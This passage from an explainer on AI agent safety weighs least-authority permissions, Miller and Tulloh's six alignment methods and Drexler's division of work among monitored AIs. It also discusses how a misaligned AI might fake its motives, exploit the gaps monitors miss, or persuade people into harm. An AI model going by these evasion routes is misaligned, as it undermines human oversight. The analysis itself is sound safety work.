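Defenders of least authority can reply that it was never supposed to remove all risk, and that the risk it leaves is limited and known. Alice knows her assistant can send at most 50 replies a day, only to people who wrote first. She can read a sample of the replies and buy insurance against mistakes.

This reply is strong when the right sets a maximum on the damage. An agent with a purse of 10 coins can lose at most 10 coins, however clever it is. The reply is weaker for text and code, because the harness limits how many messages the agent sends but not what people do after reading them. If an AI's only reader is an engineer who controls a power station, the known limit on the AI's authority is whatever that engineer can do, and the AI gets closer to that limit as it gets better at persuasion.

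Organisations can reduce the risk from persuasion by applying least authority to people as well. The engineer who talks to the AI need not control the power station, and a dangerous action can require two people who haven't read the same messages. But the AI is only useful if somebody eventually acts on its work, so some of the risk remains.

### Six ways to align an agent's decisions

Miller and Tulloh treat access rights as one of six methods that people use to get an agent to do what they want, whether the agent is an employee or a program. Peterson and colleagues later applied the scheme to AI under slightly different names. Alice could use all six:

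| Method | What Alice could do |
|---|---|
| Select the agent | Choose a model with a good record in other shops |
| Inspect its internals | Have someone check the harness and test the model |
| Allow actions | Give it the narrow rights in the earlier table |
| Explain the request | Tell it to pass questions about safety to her |
| Reward cooperation | Pay the supplier for solved problems, not for replies sent |
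| Monitor effects | Read complaints and a sample of replies |

Miller and Tulloh think critics dismiss least authority because they take "least" literally. Rights that exactly fit a task are too hard to work out in practice, so Miller and Tulloh recommend somewhat wider rights. These still permit some harmful actions but exclude the most dangerous ones, where the agent gains from harming the person it works for. For example, a supplier paid per reply gains if the assistant sends customers three messages where one would do. Alice can remove that incentive by changing the payment or limiting replies to one per question.

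The approach requires knowing what the agent stands to gain. With a hijacked AI, it is possible to make a good guess, because attackers mostly want money, data or access. A misaligned AI's aims may be unknown even to its developers, so nobody can be sure which actions to exclude.

The other methods have gaps too. Inspection works well on ordinary code but poorly on a neural network. Monitoring often finds harm only after it has happened, which is acceptable for a wrong delivery date but not for the heater. Selection depends on past behaviour, and the Foresight Institute worries that this will be a worse guide for AIs than for people. People's emotions tend to reveal their motives, while an AI might be able to fake its motives without limit.

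Combining narrow rights with monitoring still helps if they fail for different reasons. Suppose narrow rights stop 90 percent of harmful replies and monitoring stops 90 percent of the rest, so only 1 percent get through. A strong misaligned AI would concentrate on whatever both methods miss, so the actual share could be much higher.

### Drexler's division of work

Drexler proposes to stop giving whole jobs to one AI. In his January 2025 essay *AI Safety Without Trusting AI*, he divides a large project into four parts. Competing AI models propose plans and criticise them. People choose a plan, with advice from other AIs that compete to find problems. Specialised agents carry it out in small steps, each with a budget and a schedule. Further AIs monitor the results and report to people. He bases his argument that collusion can be avoided on his 2019 report, and says that Marvin Minsky, a pioneer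 of AI, urged him around 1990 to publish the idea.

This arrangement reduces the harm that each task's rights allow. An agent with one small step to do needs few rights, and a small result is often easier to check. If Alice divided her mail this way, one model could draft the answer about the heater and another could compare the draft with the manufacturer's manual before the harness sent it. The second model would need no right to send anything.

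In this arrangement, the AIs that advise people are also supposed to counter persuasion by exposing each other's misleading arguments. The trial of wardens supports this idea, since even a weaker model more than halved the success of a manipulative one. But people still made the choice the manipulative AI promoted almost a third of the time, even though the warden had no reason to side with it. Drexler's plan would use several differently trained critics, which might do better, but the trial did not test that.

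Even when a plan consists of small, checkable steps, someone has to judge whether the whole plan is good, and for a new drug or an economic policy there may be no manual to compare it with. Drexler leaves that judgement to people, who then use the rights of an entire company or government to carry out the plan. If all the advisers share a blind spot, the people deciding may have it too.

Drexler still calls further progress in alignment "extraordinarily important", partly because better-aligned AI is more useful and defence will need useful AI. He also says that a guarantee of good behaviour from one AI would not be enough, because careless or malicious people could build another. Alice's narrow permissions can't help with that problem, since they apply only to the assistant on her own computer.
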